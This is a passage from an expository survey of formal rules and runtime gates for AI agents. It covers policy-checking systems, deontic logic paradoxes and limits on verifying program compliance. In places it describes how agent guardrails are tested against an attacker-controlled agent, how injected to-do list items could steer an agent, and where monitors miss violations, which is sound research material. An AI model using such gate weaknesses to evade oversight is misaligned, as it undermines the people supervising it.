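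The 5% result has more to do with the size of the test than with the judges. The method adds an allowance of 1/(n + 1) for unseen violations, where n is the number of examples. Half of the 35 violations is 17 or 18, which puts the allowance above 5%, so even a perfect judge would have had to block everything. A 5% target needs at least 19 examples. At 10%, the same formula requires a threshold that catches every violation in the first half, which helps to explain the many false blocks. The instructions were also bare sentences without the surrounding tool calls, so the figures are weak evidence of how well a judge would recognise personal data in real emails.

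Measuring a judge on recorded runs also misses how an agent may react to a block. Ray describes two systems whose judges have the same error rates and whose runs without a gate look the same. After a block, one system stops safely and the other proposes a new violation. Only a test with the gate switched on can tell them apart.

### A rule written for each task

Sapien, the system built by Tiffany and colleagues, supplies the missing definition of "authorised" by having a language model write a new policy for every request. The model sees only the user's request and the tool documentation, so a document the agent reads later cannot influence the initial policy. A gate then checks every tool call against the policy.

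For the request "Pay my Acme invoice", a policy in simplified form would be

`list_invoices@inv . pay(vendor="Acme", amount=PREDICATE(on_invoice))`

The dot means "followed by", and `@inv` stores the result of the first call. The predicate is a short Python function that checks whether the proposed amount appears in the stored invoices. The policy rules out paying before reading the invoices, paying another company, and paying an invented amount.

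Policies are regular expressions with added data checks, so they can express the audit rule, which linear temporal logic cannot. If the user asks the agent to do everything on an online to-do list, the policy contains a gap that the policy-writing model fills once the agent has fetched the list. Anyone who can edit the list can then add tasks for the agent, but the user has in effect let the page's contents determine that part of the request.

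Some conditions are still hard to express in code, such as whether an email faithfully summarises a document. A policy can check such a condition by sending another language model a yes-or-no question about the texts involved. The model's answer can only restrict what the rest of the policy permits. If an attacker fools this model, the agent may send a bad summary, but still only to the recipient the policy names.

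Tiffany and colleagues tested Sapien with four recent models from Google and Anthropic. On AgentDojo's 97 tasks, agents completed one to five fewer tasks with a policy than without one. To test security, the researchers assumed that an attacker already controlled the agent and that the second language model always gave the answer the attacker wanted. They then checked whether the policy permitted any sequence of calls that achieved the attacker's goal.

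| Benchmark | Attacks ruled out by Sapien | Attacks ruled out by a list of permitted tools |
|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, four models | 93.2–95.2% | 82.7–86.8% |
| Toolathlon, Gemini 3.8 Flash | 64.6% | 32.4% |

Toolathlon's tasks are longer, and the attackers' goals there involved tools that the task required, so a list of permitted tools was much less useful.

Some policies blocked legitimate work because the model had guessed the data incorrectly. One policy required "London Luxury Hotel" where the database had "London Luxury". These errors are separate from the more general problem of models mistranslating rules written in English. Sapien also does not define harm. If a user asks for help with a fraudulent email, the policy permits the steps needed to write it. A vague request produces a permissive policy. Tiffany and colleagues leave harmful requests to other safeguards.

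### Domains with agreed definitions

In a narrow enough setting, people may agree on a definition or adopt one. A company can declare that certain columns of its customer database are personal data. The rule "no email contains personal data" then becomes a version of the influence rule: no value from these columns may reach an external email. A gate that tracks where values come from can enforce this. The definition covers paraphrases and summaries if the gate can track values through them. It misses personal details that a customer types into an ordinary message, so a company might combine it with a classifier for free text.

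Dalrymple and colleagues list other cases of this kind, including machines that nobody can log in to without the right credentials and DNA synthesisers that cannot produce listed pathogens. Sometimes a whole system is easier to specify than its parts. For example, nobody can formally define what it means for a camera to recognise a pedestrian correctly, but a rule for a self-driving car can require it to keep a certain distance from every pedestrian.

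A substitute definition can also fail when a capable system optimises against it. If an assistant earns a reward for every email that contains no listed field, it may learn to convey the same facts in other words. Dalrymple and colleagues warn that a measure that tracks harm well in normal situations may stop doing so once a system optimises for it.

### The dispute over Guaranteed Safe AI

Dalrymple and colleagues want to extend formal guarantees to much broader requirements. They call an approach Guaranteed Safe AI if it has three parts: a world model that describes how an AI system's actions affect its surroundings, a specification of which effects are acceptable, and a verifier that proves the specification holds or bounds the probability of a violation. They grade specifications by how much safety each kind would provide if it succeeded.

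| Level | Specification |
|---|---|
| 0 | None |
| 1 | People judge the system by their intuitions |
| 2 | Rules in ordinary language, which an opaque AI system interprets |
| 3 | Hand-written formal rules for limited properties |
| 4 | Formal rules in which neural networks supply the meaning of some concepts |
| 5 | Formal rules composed of parts that AI writes and people audit |
| 6 | Hand-written formal rules for comprehensive safety properties |
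| 7 | A complete account of everything people want in every context |

Critics argue that moving from limited to comprehensive properties is far harder than the scale suggests. Proving that an attacker cannot break into a program is difficult but well defined, because the specification concerns only that program. To prove that the program cannot damage any other system, the world model would have to describe every system the program might reach, including bugs that nobody knows about. An ordinary series of database queries might trigger such a bug in a server on the other side of the world. The same difficulty arises in moving from "this machine will not make any of these listed pathogens" to "nothing this machine makes will endanger human health".

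A second objection is that biology and human behaviour have no complete set of formal laws from which to build a world model. Defenders answer that known physics already covers everything in ordinary human experience, and that engineers have formal models of fluids, materials and circuits. But knowing the basic laws does not guarantee that we can derive their consequences. Dalrymple and colleagues themselves note that physics alone cannot determine whether a molecule is toxic, because toxicity also depends on facts about human cells. For human behaviour, they suggest models that allow a range of possible actions, with a proof that covers all of them. This is sound, but as the range of human actions widens, the system will be able to prove fewer of its own useful actions safe.

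They also argue that the objection applies to every approach to safety, because any method relies on beliefs about the world, and a world model makes those beliefs explicit. The guarantee can also account for errors in the model. If the model is wrong with a probability of at most ε at each step, a guarantee over n steps holds in reality with a probability of at least $(1-\varepsilon)^n$. With an error rate of one in a thousand, this lower bound falls to about 37% after 1,000 steps, so long-running agents would need extremely accurate models. The reply also does not solve the problem of definitions. A perfectly accurate world model could predict that Bob will suffer a minor injury, but that prediction would not determine the default used to decide whether the injury counts as harm.

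Some defenders of safety proofs aim only to prove that software, cryptography and hardware can withstand attacks by AI systems, not that an advanced AI system will always behave well. This avoids a general definition of harm, since each component needs only its own specification. Critics reply that a hostile system could act outside the protected infrastructure, so such proofs would be at most one part of a defence. Dalrymple and colleagues expect AI to make specifications easier to write, for example by finding cases in which two candidate definitions give different results. Those cases could help a committee see what it has to decide.

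By 2026, researchers had built working systems mainly at the narrow end of this programme. Ray describes recent runtime guardrails for agents, including Agent-C, as instances of it. FORGE and Agent-C enforce hand-written rules about limited properties, which corresponds to level 3. A language model drafts Soteria's rules and people check them, a process that resembles level 5, but these rules also cover only limited properties. Sapien does not fit the scale neatly, because its policies are formal but no person audits them. All four systems constrain tool calls, and none has a world model that predicts how an email will affect its reader.

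## Duties, exceptions and what to do after a violation

The assistant's duty to report any breach of a rule applies only after a breach, so a specification that includes this duty has to make sense even when a rule has been broken. Philosophers call this a contrary-to-duty obligation. *Logical Modalities within the European AI Act* (2025) finds such obligations in the EU's AI Act, including in Article 20, which requires a provider to correct, withdraw, disable or recall a high-risk system that does not conform to the Act. One party's violation can also create a duty for another. If an organisation that assesses AI systems fails to meet its own obligations, the authority that appointed it has to act.

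### Reading "ought" as "is true"

Suppose the policy forbids leaks of customer data and requires a breach notice after any leak. The obvious formulas are

$$\forall e\,\neg\text{Leak}(e) \qquad\text{and}\qquad \forall e\,\big(\text{Leak}(e) \rightarrow \exists f\,(e<f \wedge \text{Notice}(f))\big).$$

The ban on leaks logically implies the notice rule, because an implication is true whenever its "if" part is false. For the same reason, the ban also implies "after any leak, delete the log". If we add the fact that e5 was a leak, the premises contradict each other, and every sentence follows from a contradiction.

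A monitor that evaluates each formula separately does not have this problem. Given a log with a leak and a later notice, it correctly reports that the log violates the ban but satisfies the notice rule. The problem arises when a program uses the rules as premises. A planner could not work out from them what to do after a leak, and a prover that assumed the ban while verifying the notice rule would approve an assistant that never sends notices.

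### Chisholm's paradox

Deontic logic, the logic of obligation and permission, has an operator for "it ought to be that", written Ob here. In the standard system, each possible world has a set of ideal worlds, in which everything is as it ought to be. Ob p is true at a world when p holds in all of its ideal worlds. Axiom D guarantees that each world has at least one ideal world, so p and ¬p cannot both be obligatory.

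In 1963 Roderick Chisholm published four sentences that this system cannot handle. Here is a version about a data leak, with l for "the assistant leaks data" and n for "the assistant sends a breach notice".

| Sentence | Formula |
|---|---|
| The assistant ought not to leak data | Ob ¬l |
| It ought to be that if the assistant does not leak data, it sends no notice | Ob(¬l → ¬n) |
| If the assistant leaks data, it ought to send a notice | l → Ob n |
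| The assistant leaks data | l |

The formulas are inconsistent, even though the situation is ordinary and the sentences seem consistent. The first two formulas imply that every ideal world has no leak and therefore no notice, so Ob ¬n holds. The last two imply Ob n. By axiom D there is an ideal world, and it would have to contain both a notice and no notice.

The Internet Encyclopedia of Philosophy's *Contrary-to-Duty Paradox* discusses the quick repairs. Writing the false-alarm rule as ¬l → Ob ¬n removes the contradiction, but that formula follows from l alone. Writing the notice rule as Ob(l → n) also removes it, but that formula follows from the ban on leaks. In English, neither rule follows from the other sentences. Dropping axiom D leaves the assistant with two conflicting duties. No world can satisfy both, so there are no ideal worlds and everything becomes obligatory. The original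 formulas also imply Ob(¬l ∧ n), a duty to leak nothing and to send a notice of a leak.

### The same contradiction in first-order logic

Standard deontic logic translates into first-order logic if worlds are objects. Let Ideal(w, v) mean that v is ideal from the standpoint of w. The four sentences and axiom D become

$$\begin{aligned}
&\forall v\,(\text{Ideal}(w,v) \rightarrow \neg\text{Leak}(v))\\
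&\forall v\,(\text{Ideal}(w,v) \rightarrow (\neg\text{Leak}(v) \rightarrow \neg\text{Notice}(v)))\\
&\text{Leak}(w) \rightarrow \forall v\,(\text{Ideal}(w,v) \rightarrow \text{Notice}(v))\\
&\text{Leak}(w)\\
&\exists v\;\text{Ideal}(w,v).
\end{aligned}$$

The contradiction remains, so a lack of expressive power is not the cause. The model divides worlds only into ideal and non-ideal ones. A world where a leak is reported and a world where it is concealed are both non-ideal, although the notice rule exists to distinguish them.

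Ranking the worlds makes this distinction possible. From best to worst, the ranking could be:

1. No leak, no notice
2. No leak, but a false notice
3. A leak, with a notice
4. A leak, without a notice

Write Ob(q/p) for "given p, it ought to be that q", and count it as true when the best worlds with p are all worlds with q. Then Ob(¬l/⊤) is true, where ⊤ stands for no condition at all, because the best world has no leak. Ob(¬n/¬l) is true because the best world without a leak has no notice, and Ob(n/l) is true because the best world with a leak has one. All three remain true if the assistant leaks data. With a relation ≥ for "at least as good as", this reading is first-order too:

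$$\exists v\,\big(p(v) \wedge q(v) \wedge \forall u\,(u \ge v \wedge p(u) \rightarrow q(u))\big).$$

An assistant that has leaked data still needs to know what to do now, but l and Ob(n/l) no longer imply Ob n. The Stanford Encyclopedia of Philosophy's *A Bit More on Chisholm's Paradox* explains why we cannot allow this inference in every case. Suppose a rule requires that if the assistant leaks a file, it leaks only one page. If the inference always held, an assistant that is going to leak the file tomorrow would have a duty to leak a page, even though it could still leak nothing.

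A common compromise allows the inference only when p is settled. This is easy to apply to an agent with a log, since past events can't be undone. The assistant has to send a notice only after a leak, and until then its only relevant duty is to leak nothing.

Giving each duty a time does not solve every case, because the duties and the violation can all concern the same moment. In an example from Henry Prakken and Marek Sergot, a neighbourhood has dogs but ought to have none. If there are no dogs, there ought to be no warning signs, and if there are dogs, there ought to be warning signs.

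Broersen, Gabbay and colleagues (2013), in *Deontic Logic*, call the name "standard deontic logic" a misnomer because researchers no longer treat the system as a standard, but its axioms remain in use. *PolicyKG* (2026), a system that uses language models to translate institutional policies into formal rules, combines these axioms with first-order logic. An audit of one institution's policies found the combined language sufficient, a result the paper calls "a lower bound, not a proof". Even if the language could express every policy, Chisholm's problem would remain, because each of his sentences has a formula and the contradiction appears only when one reasons from them together.

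### Recording breaches

For the reporting duty itself, a simpler approach is to make the names of rules into objects and let Breach(e, r) mean that event e breaks rule r. Broersen and colleagues describe a related method, which treats a ban on an action as the statement that performing it leads to a violation. The policy becomes a set of definitions:

$$\begin{aligned}
\text{Breach}(e,\textit{leak}) &\leftrightarrow \text{Leak}(e)\\
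\text{Breach}(e,\textit{report}) &\leftrightarrow \exists r\,(r\neq\textit{report} \wedge \text{Breach}(e,r)) \wedge \neg\exists f\,(e<f \wedge \text{Report}(f,e)).
\end{aligned}$$

A leak no longer causes a contradiction. A reported leak counts as one breach and an unreported leak as two, which is how most people would count them. The definition needs the condition r ≠ *report* because "any breach of a rule" would otherwise include breaches of the reporting duty itself. An unreported event that broke no other rule would then break the reporting duty if and only if it broke the reporting duty, so the definition would not determine whether it did.

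When an assistant rarely breaks rules, its operators have little evidence about what it does after breaking one. *Formal Ethical Obligations in Reinforcement Learning Agents* (2024) addresses this by forcing an agent to violate its main duty, then checking whether the agent meets its follow-up duty from the resulting state. Operators could check the reporting duty the same way, by simulating a leak in a test environment.

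*Deontic Policies for Runtime Governance of Agentic AI Systems* (Joshi, Finin and colleagues, 2026) describes AgenticRei, a prototype gate that keeps track of duties. When it permits an agent to install software, for example, it registers a duty to notify the head of information security, sets a deadline, and alerts someone if the deadline passes. The gate always registers the duty, but it can only monitor whether the agent fulfils it. According to Joshi and colleagues, two widely used policy languages, Rego and Cedar, have no construct for obligations, so policy writers must add separate rules that look for the required event. This is more an inconvenience for them than a limit on what logic can express, because "Every installation is followed by a notification" has the same form as the answer rule.

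### Can temporal logic represent norms?

Governatori (2014), in *Thou Shalt is not You Will*, argues that LTL might be unsuitable for real norms. His example is a fictional privacy act based on Australian law:

- Collecting personal information is forbidden without a court order.
- Destroying illegally collected personal information before accessing it excuses the collection.
- Collecting medical information is forbidden unless the collector is permitted to collect personal information.

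He translates "forbidden" as "never happens" and "permitted" as "eventually happens". Spelled out in the usual operators, his formulas are

$$\begin{aligned}
&\neg\text{Order} \rightarrow \big(\mathsf{G}\,\neg\text{Collect} \vee \mathsf{F}(\text{Collect} \wedge \mathsf{F}\,\text{Destroy})\big)\\
&\text{Order} \rightarrow \mathsf{F}\,\text{Collect}\\
&\mathsf{G}\,\neg\text{Collect} \rightarrow \mathsf{G}\,\neg\text{Medical}\\
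&\mathsf{F}\,\text{Collect} \rightarrow \mathsf{F}\,\text{Medical}.
\end{aligned}$$

Suppose someone without a court order collects both kinds of information at once and then destroys the personal information. All four formulas are true at every step, yet collecting the medical information was illegal. About a dozen legal professionals whom Governatori asked agreed that this was illegal.

Alechina, Dastani and Logan (2016), in *Expressibility of Norms in Temporal Logic*, reply that the translation is at fault, because "permitted" does not mean "will happen". They use ordinary LTL formulas to sort all possible runs into three classes. The first formula is slightly shortened here.

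| Class | Formula |
|---|---|
| Fully compliant | $\mathsf{G}(\text{Order} \vee (\neg\text{Collect} \wedge \neg\text{Medical}))$ |
| Weakly compliant | $\mathsf{F}(\neg\text{Order} \wedge \text{Collect}) \wedge \mathsf{G}(\neg\text{Order} \wedge \text{Collect} \rightarrow \mathsf{F}\,\text{Destroy}) \wedge \mathsf{G}(\neg\text{Order} \rightarrow \neg\text{Medical})$ |
| Violating | $\mathsf{F}(\neg\text{Order} \wedge (\text{Medical} \vee (\text{Collect} \wedge \neg\mathsf{F}\,\text{Destroy})))$ |

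Every run belongs to exactly one class. Trying both sets of formulas on five runs shows how far apart they are.

| Run | Class according to Alechina and colleagues | Governatori's formulas all true? |
|---|---|---|
| No order, nothing collected | Fully compliant | Yes |
| Order throughout, nothing collected | Fully compliant | No |
| No order, personal information collected and destroyed | Weakly compliant | No |
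| No order, personal information collected and kept | Violating | No |
| No order, both kinds collected, personal information destroyed | Violating | Yes |

Governatori's formulas give the wrong result in three of the five cases. They classify his own example as compliant, and they classify someone who obtains a court order but never uses it as non-compliant. They also classify someone who makes amends for collecting personal information as non-compliant, because that person never collects medical information.

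So LTL can state which runs comply with the act. Governatori had conceded that his example shows only that one formalisation fails. But he objected that working out the compliant runs first and then deriving formulas from them would be useless, because people would already have done the legal reasoning and a system would always pass a test derived from its own runs. The formulas in the reply come from the act, not from any system's runs, so a system can fail them.

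The complaint about legal reasoning is stronger. The act's rule on medical information depends on whether collecting personal information is permitted, but in the formulas it depends directly on a court order, because a person has already worked out that only an order gives permission. If parliament later allowed collection with the customer's consent, the act's rule would need no amendment, but someone would have to change the formulas wherever Order appears. Defining a symbol Permitted once and using it throughout would confine the change to one place.

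The reply also treats compensation very roughly. If the assistant collects Ana's data, then Ben's, and destroys only Ben's, both collections count as compensated under the formula, because Destroy has no argument to identify the data. A first-order formula can require the assistant to destroy the same data it collected. Alechina and colleagues themselves suggest replacing Destroy with "not read until destroyed" and note that a real rule would set a deadline.

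The three formulas also do not rank the classes. Governatori regards a compensated violation as legal but less ideal than no violation. An assistant that only avoids violating runs has no reason to prefer never collecting data illegally over collecting it every day and destroying it every night. A gate can enforce the two duties separately, by blocking every unauthorised collection and requiring the data to be destroyed if one happens anyway. An assistant that plans for itself needs a ranking like the one used for Chisholm's sentences. The reporting duty is different because a report does not excuse the leak. Governatori also allows for duties that arise from a violation without compensating for it.

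### Exceptions

First-order consequence is monotonic, which means that adding a premise never removes a conclusion. Any structure that makes the larger set of premises true also makes the smaller set true, so whatever followed before still follows. Rules with exceptions work differently. Take three rules about customer files:

- **General ban:** exporting a file is forbidden.
- **Approval rule:** exporting a file with the data officer's approval is permitted.
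- **Seal rule:** exporting a file that a court has sealed is forbidden.

If we write the export rules as ordinary implications, every approved export is both forbidden and not forbidden. Defeasible rules avoid this contradiction because each rule holds unless a stronger one overrides it. We can have the seal rule override the approval rule, and the approval rule override the general ban.

| Known facts about the export | Rules that apply | Conclusion |
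|---|---|---|
| None | General ban | Forbidden |
| Approved | General ban, approval rule | Permitted |
| Approved, file sealed | All three | Forbidden |

Each new fact withdraws the previous conclusion, which no set of first-order premises allows. First-order logic can still define the final result:

$$\text{Forbidden}(e) \leftrightarrow \text{Export}(e) \wedge (\neg\text{Approved}(e) \vee \text{Sealed}(e)).$$

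Governatori uses the same method, adding the negation of each exception to the rule it overrides, so every new exception requires a change to an old rule. The definition also needs complete information. If the premises don't establish whether anyone approved the export, neither "forbidden" nor "not forbidden" follows from them. A gate can be programmed to treat the export as unapproved unless an approval is on record, as in FORGE's Datalog. *Modeling Deontic Modal Logic in ASP* (2025) uses answer set programming, a rule language with separate negations for "no approval is on record" and "the officer refused approval". It represents obligations as constraints that apply only under stated conditions, and presents this as a way to resolve the contrary-to-duty paradox.

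*Reinforcement Learning Guided by Provable Normative Compliance* (2022) uses defeasible deontic logic to guide learning agents. Besides defeasible rules, this logic has strict rules, which allow no exceptions, and defeaters, which can block a conclusion but cannot establish its opposite. The program SPINdle computes which conclusions are provable.

AgenticRei also has priorities. In one example policy, a company forbids exports of regulated data, but a higher-priority permission allows them for agents with a credential from a named compliance authority. The prototype only simulates checking the credential's signature. In Cedar, a prohibition always overrides a permission, so the policy's author would have to write the exception into the prohibition. Priorities have to come from someone with the authority to set them. If two conflicting rules apply and neither has priority, defeasible logic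 draws neither conclusion, so a gate needs a default, such as blocking the action.

### "Change nothing else"

Suppose a user asks the assistant to cancel reservation R9 and change nothing else. If the database has ten relations, ten first-order clauses can require that entries unrelated to R9 stay the same. A version that covers every property, including unlisted ones, quantifies over predicates, which first-order logic does not allow. The literal request is also too strict, because a cancellation should trigger a refund. The user wants the smallest set of changes that a cancellation involves.

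McCarthy (1986), in *Applications of Circumscription to Formalizing Common Sense Knowledge*, applies a method called circumscription to this kind of problem. It assumes that as few things as possible are abnormal, and here "abnormal" can mean "changed". Let A(S) be a formula that collects what we know about the set of changed records, with S standing for that set. Circumscription adds that no smaller set would fit:

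$$A(\text{Changed}) \wedge \forall S\,\big[A(S) \wedge \forall x\,(S(x)\rightarrow\text{Changed}(x)) \rightarrow \forall x\,(\text{Changed}(x)\rightarrow S(x))\big].$$

S ranges over sets of records, so the formula is second-order. It reduces to a first-order one in simple cases. Suppose all we know is that cancelling R9 changes R9 and its payment record P9. Then A(S) is $\forall x\,(x=\text{R9} \vee x=\text{P9} \rightarrow S(x))$. The set containing just these two records fits, and every other set that fits contains it, so circumscription gives

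$$\forall x\,(\text{Changed}(x) \leftrightarrow x=\text{R9} \vee x=\text{P9}).$$

The same argument works whenever A(S) has the form $\forall x\,(\varphi(x)\rightarrow S(x))$ and φ mentions neither S nor Changed.

The reduction fails when changes spread. If a change to one record can trigger changes to others, A(S) becomes

$$S(\text{R9}) \wedge \forall x\forall y\,(S(x) \wedge \text{Triggers}(x,y) \rightarrow S(y)).$$

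The smallest such set contains R9 and everything that a chain of triggers connects to it. This is the transitive closure again, and no first-order formula about Triggers defines it for databases of every size.

There may also be more than one minimal change. If the assistant has to free one seat on a full flight, cancelling any single booking is a minimal change, and circumscription provides no basis for choosing between passengers.

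### Don't disturb, and restore

Weld and Etzioni (1994), in *The First Law of Robotics*, avoided minimisation in an early proposal for software agents. Their agent has instructions to bring disk use below 90%, and the danger is that it deletes irreplaceable documents. Instead of defining harm, they let users list conditions that the agent must not disturb. A plan satisfies dont-disturb(C) if every instance of C that is true at the start is still true after each action:

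$$\forall j\,\forall x\,\big(C(x,0) \rightarrow C(x,j)\big).$$

This constraint is first-order because the user names C. It is weaker than "C always holds", since the agent does not have to fix violations that existed before it started. An agent that does nothing therefore satisfies any collection of these constraints, so every such collection is consistent. If constraints on behaviour are unrestricted, no procedure can decide in every case whether they are consistent. A user can freeze a predicate P completely by protecting both P(x) and ¬P(x).

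In the disk example, C(f) is "f is on tape or f is still a file". Deleting paper.tex makes the second half false, so the deletion violates the constraint unless the paper is on tape. The planner can back up the paper first or look for another way to free space. If every way of freeing space violates the constraint, the agent must refuse the request. The time needed to check one effect of an action against a constraint grows only in proportion to the constraint's length.

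Some conditions only need to hold again at the end. An agent that searches old mail may have to decompress files, and restore(compressed(f)) requires it to compress them again afterwards. Dont-disturb constraints take priority over the user's goal, which takes priority over restore constraints. The planner first finds a way to reach the goal and then adds steps to clean up, dropping any it cannot achieve. It can therefore leave a mess that a different plan would have avoided. Weld and Etzioni accept this because most actions in software are easy to reverse, although some, such as sending an email, are not.

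They also assume that the agent knows the initial state completely, that nobody else changes anything, and that the description of each action lists every predicate the action affects. If the cancellation tool also emails the customer and its description omits this, the planner will approve a cancellation even when a constraint forbids contacting the customer.

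## Requirements that can be stated exactly but not checked

Even if every word in a rule is defined and every tool does exactly what its description states, there may be no procedure that determines whether a program obeys the rule. The gatekeeper in Pérez-Acle's preprint, which must accept or reject whole programs before they run, has this problem even though it has the rule, the code and no time limit.

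### Three rules in arithmetic

The objects are the natural numbers. Every program is a finite text, so we can number the programs and let p stand for one of them. Three relations describe what programs do:

- B(p, t), as before, means that p performs the forbidden operation within t steps on input 0.
- E(p, h, j, a, t) means that p, started with the secret bit h, publishes the value a in position j within t steps.
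- A(p, n, t) means that p answers request n within t steps.

As with B, running p for t steps settles any single instance of E or A. Gödel's method of encoding lists as numbers, which also worked for chains of influence, lets a formula with only addition and multiplication describe such a run. The three rules are then first-order formulas of arithmetic:

$$\begin{aligned}
&\forall t\;\neg B(p,t)\\
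&\forall j\,\forall a\,\forall t\,\exists u\,\big[(E(p,0,j,a,t)\rightarrow E(p,1,j,a,u)) \wedge (E(p,1,j,a,t)\rightarrow E(p,0,j,a,u))\big]\\
&\forall n\,\exists t\;A(p,n,t)
\end{aligned}$$

The first formula expresses the ban on the forbidden operation. The second expresses a secrecy rule, which requires p to publish the same values in the same order whether the secret is 0 or 1. The third expresses the answer rule. Over the natural numbers, each formula is true of exactly the programs that obey the rule it expresses.

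No fixed language, including that of arithmetic, can express every rule. Pérez-Acle shows this with Cantor's diagonal argument. A language has only countably many descriptions, so we can list the sets of programs it describes. For each set on the list, we pick a different program and permit it exactly when the set does not contain it. The set of permitted programs then differs from every set on the list. We also pick a second program for each set and forbid it exactly when the set does not contain it, so the set of forbidden programs differs from every set on the list too. He cautions that this argument does not identify any rule of practical interest. It also does not produce a rule that no language can express, since a new language could include a symbol for the missing set.

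### What a procedure can confirm

The three rules above can be written as formulas, but the halting problem limits our ability to check them. Suppose a program D could decide, for every program e and input w, whether e halts on w. We could then write a program G that takes a number n and uses D to find out whether program n halts on input n. G loops forever if program n halts on input n, and halts otherwise. Let g be G's number. Since program g is G, G halts on input g exactly when G does not halt on input g. This is a contradiction, so D cannot exist.

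We can still confirm that e halts on w by running it and waiting, but no procedure can confirm non-halting in every case. If one existed, we could alternate between the two procedures until one accepted, and that would decide halting, which is impossible.

The ban on the forbidden operation has the same problem. For any e and w, let p be the program that runs e on w with no visible effect and performs the forbidden operation if that run halts. Then p obeys the ban exactly when e never halts on w, so a procedure that confirmed every compliant program would also confirm every case of non-halting. Violations of the ban are the only cases that a procedure can always confirm. Alfonseca and colleagues published this construction in 2021 to argue that nobody can guarantee the containment of a superintelligent system.

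Whether a program complies can also depend on an open question in mathematics. Goldbach's conjecture is that every even number from 4 upwards is the sum of two primes. A program that tests 4, 6, 8 and so on, and performs the forbidden operation if it finds a counterexample, obeys the ban exactly when the conjecture is true. Nobody has found a counterexample below $4 \times 10^{18}$, but that does not settle whether the program complies.

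For the other two rules, Pérez-Acle proves that neither compliance nor violation is confirmable. He builds four more programs from e and w.

| Program | If e never halts on w | If e halts on w | What is not confirmable |
|---|---|---|---|
| Run e on w, then publish the secret | Obeys the secrecy rule, because it publishes nothing | Breaks it | Compliance with the secrecy rule |
| If the secret is 0, publish 0. If it is 1, run e on w, then publish 0 | Breaks the secrecy rule, because it publishes only when the secret is 0 | Obeys it | Violation of the secrecy rule |
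| On request n, run e on w for n steps. Answer if it has not halted, and otherwise loop forever | Obeys the answer rule | Breaks it, because it ignores all requests from some number on | Compliance with the answer rule |
| On any request, run e on w, then answer | Breaks the answer rule | Obeys it | Violation of the answer rule |

The quantifiers show why these rules are harder than the ban. A single value of t can refute the first formula. Refuting the third requires finding a request that the program never answers, and no finite wait can show that an answer will never come. Establishing it requires checking infinitely many requests. The secrecy formula also has a "there is" after a "for all". Pérez-Acle proves that no rewriting removes the difference between these two rules and the ban. An imaginary machine that could answer every halting question could decide the ban, but not the other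 two.

The result for secrecy depends on what an observer can see. In this model the observer sees the published values but not when they appear, so it cannot tell whether a program has stopped or is just slow. If the rule also required the outputs to agree at every step, as observational determinism does, it would be possible to confirm violations but not compliance.

### What finite evidence can establish

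Pérez-Acle also characterises the confirmable categories for rules that depend only on what a program visibly does. A finite record gives a program's first few visible actions on each of finitely many inputs, and a program matches the record if its behaviour on those inputs begins that way. He proves that a category is confirmable exactly when it consists of the programs that match at least one record in a set that some procedure can list. The programs that break the ban form such a category, because each matches a record that ends with the forbidden operation.

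If a category has such a collection of records, a procedure can run a candidate program on the recorded inputs and accept it once its outputs match a record. Conversely, if a category has no such collection, a procedure that accepted exactly the programs in it would let us confirm that a program never halts.

- **More behaviour can take a program out of the category.** Suppose p is in the category, and q does everything that p does and then something more that takes it out. Build a program that behaves like p while it runs e on w in the background, and that continues like q if e halts. This program is in the category exactly when e never halts.
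- **No finite part of a program's behaviour is enough.** Suppose p is in the category, but a program that showed only a finite part of p's behaviour would not be. Build a program that copies p until it finds that e has halted and then falls silent. On input n, it checks the first n steps of e before it does anything, so if e halts, it shows only a finite part of p's behaviour. It is in the category exactly when e never halts.

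Compliance with the ban fails in the first way, because a program that has done nothing so far will comply if it stays idle but could still perform the operation later. Compliance with the answer rule fails in the second way, because a finite record covers only finitely many requests.

The theorem implies that no rule about visible behaviour is decidable if it permits some programs and forbids others. One side of any such rule contains the silent program, which runs forever without doing anything visible. Every other program does everything the silent program does and possibly more, so that side is not confirmable, and the rule is therefore not decidable. Henry Rice proved the corresponding undecidability result in 1953 for properties of the function that a program computes, and the Rice–Shapiro theorem describes which of those properties are confirmable. Pérez-Acle extends both results to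 the actions and outputs a program produces while it runs, and he describes the ingredients of his proofs as classical.

A policy writer can use the theorem when choosing how to phrase a requirement. "On input 0, log an audit before writing anything" is confirmable if it requires the program to log the audit, because once the program has done so, nothing it does later can break the rule. The lookup rule isn't confirmable, because a program can also obey it by never cancelling a reservation. Requiring every program to make a lookup first would make compliance on a given input confirmable, but it would also rule out programs that make no lookup because they don't need one.

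### The compliant program that every checker misses

A gatekeeper might settle for a checker that accepts some compliant programs and never accepts a non-compliant one. Suppose the checker accepts a program only on the basis of a certificate, which is finite evidence, such as a proof, that it can test in finite time. Pérez-Acle proves that a set of programs is confirmable exactly when some checker of this kind accepts every program in the set and no others. Every such checker for the ban therefore fails to accept some compliant program, and he shows how to construct such a program.

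Let V be the checker, which never accepts a program that breaks the ban. The program q searches all possible certificates for one that would make V accept q itself, and performs the forbidden operation if it finds one. (A theorem by Stephen Kleene guarantees that a program can refer to its own text in this way.) If V accepted q on the basis of some certificate, q would find that certificate and break the ban, but V never accepts such a program. So V does not accept q, even though q complies with the ban, because its search never ends and it never performs the operation.

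The program q is longer than V by at most a fixed amount of code, so V's failure to accept q does not depend on q being very long. Pérez-Acle built q for four simple checkers of 64 to 409 characters, and the extra code was 938 to 949 characters long. None of the checkers accepted its q, and none of the four programs performed the operation in 100,000 steps. He gives similar constructions for complying with and violating the other two rules.

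V can be extended to accept q. The extended checker is still never wrong, but the same construction gives a new compliant program that it misses. After any finite number of such additions, the checker still misses infinitely many compliant programs. If it missed only finitely many, adding them to its list would produce a checker that accepts every compliant program and no others, which is impossible.

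Panigrahy and Sharan (2025), in *Limitations on Safe, Trusted, Artificial General Intelligence*, use a similar construction to reach a stronger conclusion, that no AI system is safe, trusted and an AGI at once. They call a system safe if it never makes a false claim, although it may answer "don't know", trusted if people assume it is safe, and an AGI if it can solve every problem to which a person has a provably correct solution. In the simplest version of the proof, the system always gives some answer. Their program runs the system on the program's own text to find out whether the program always halts, then loops forever if the answer is yes and stops otherwise. A safe system cannot answer yes, because the program would then loop forever and the answer would be false. The program therefore stops, and a person who trusts the system can prove this in a few lines, although the system itself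 cannot give the correct answer.

The person's proof assumes that the system never makes a false claim. A second system with the same assumption could give the same proof, so the theorem limits what a system can establish about programs that refer to that system, not what machines can prove in general. Panigrahy and Sharan say they do not aim to separate human reasoning from every AI system. Their definitions are strict, so a system that was wrong about one program in a billion would not count as safe.

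### Time limits

The ban becomes decidable if it covers only the first T steps. A checker can run the program for T steps in a sandbox and see whether it performs the forbidden operation. Pérez-Acle proves that a checker that is always right cannot be much faster than this on every program, even if it reads the code instead of running it.

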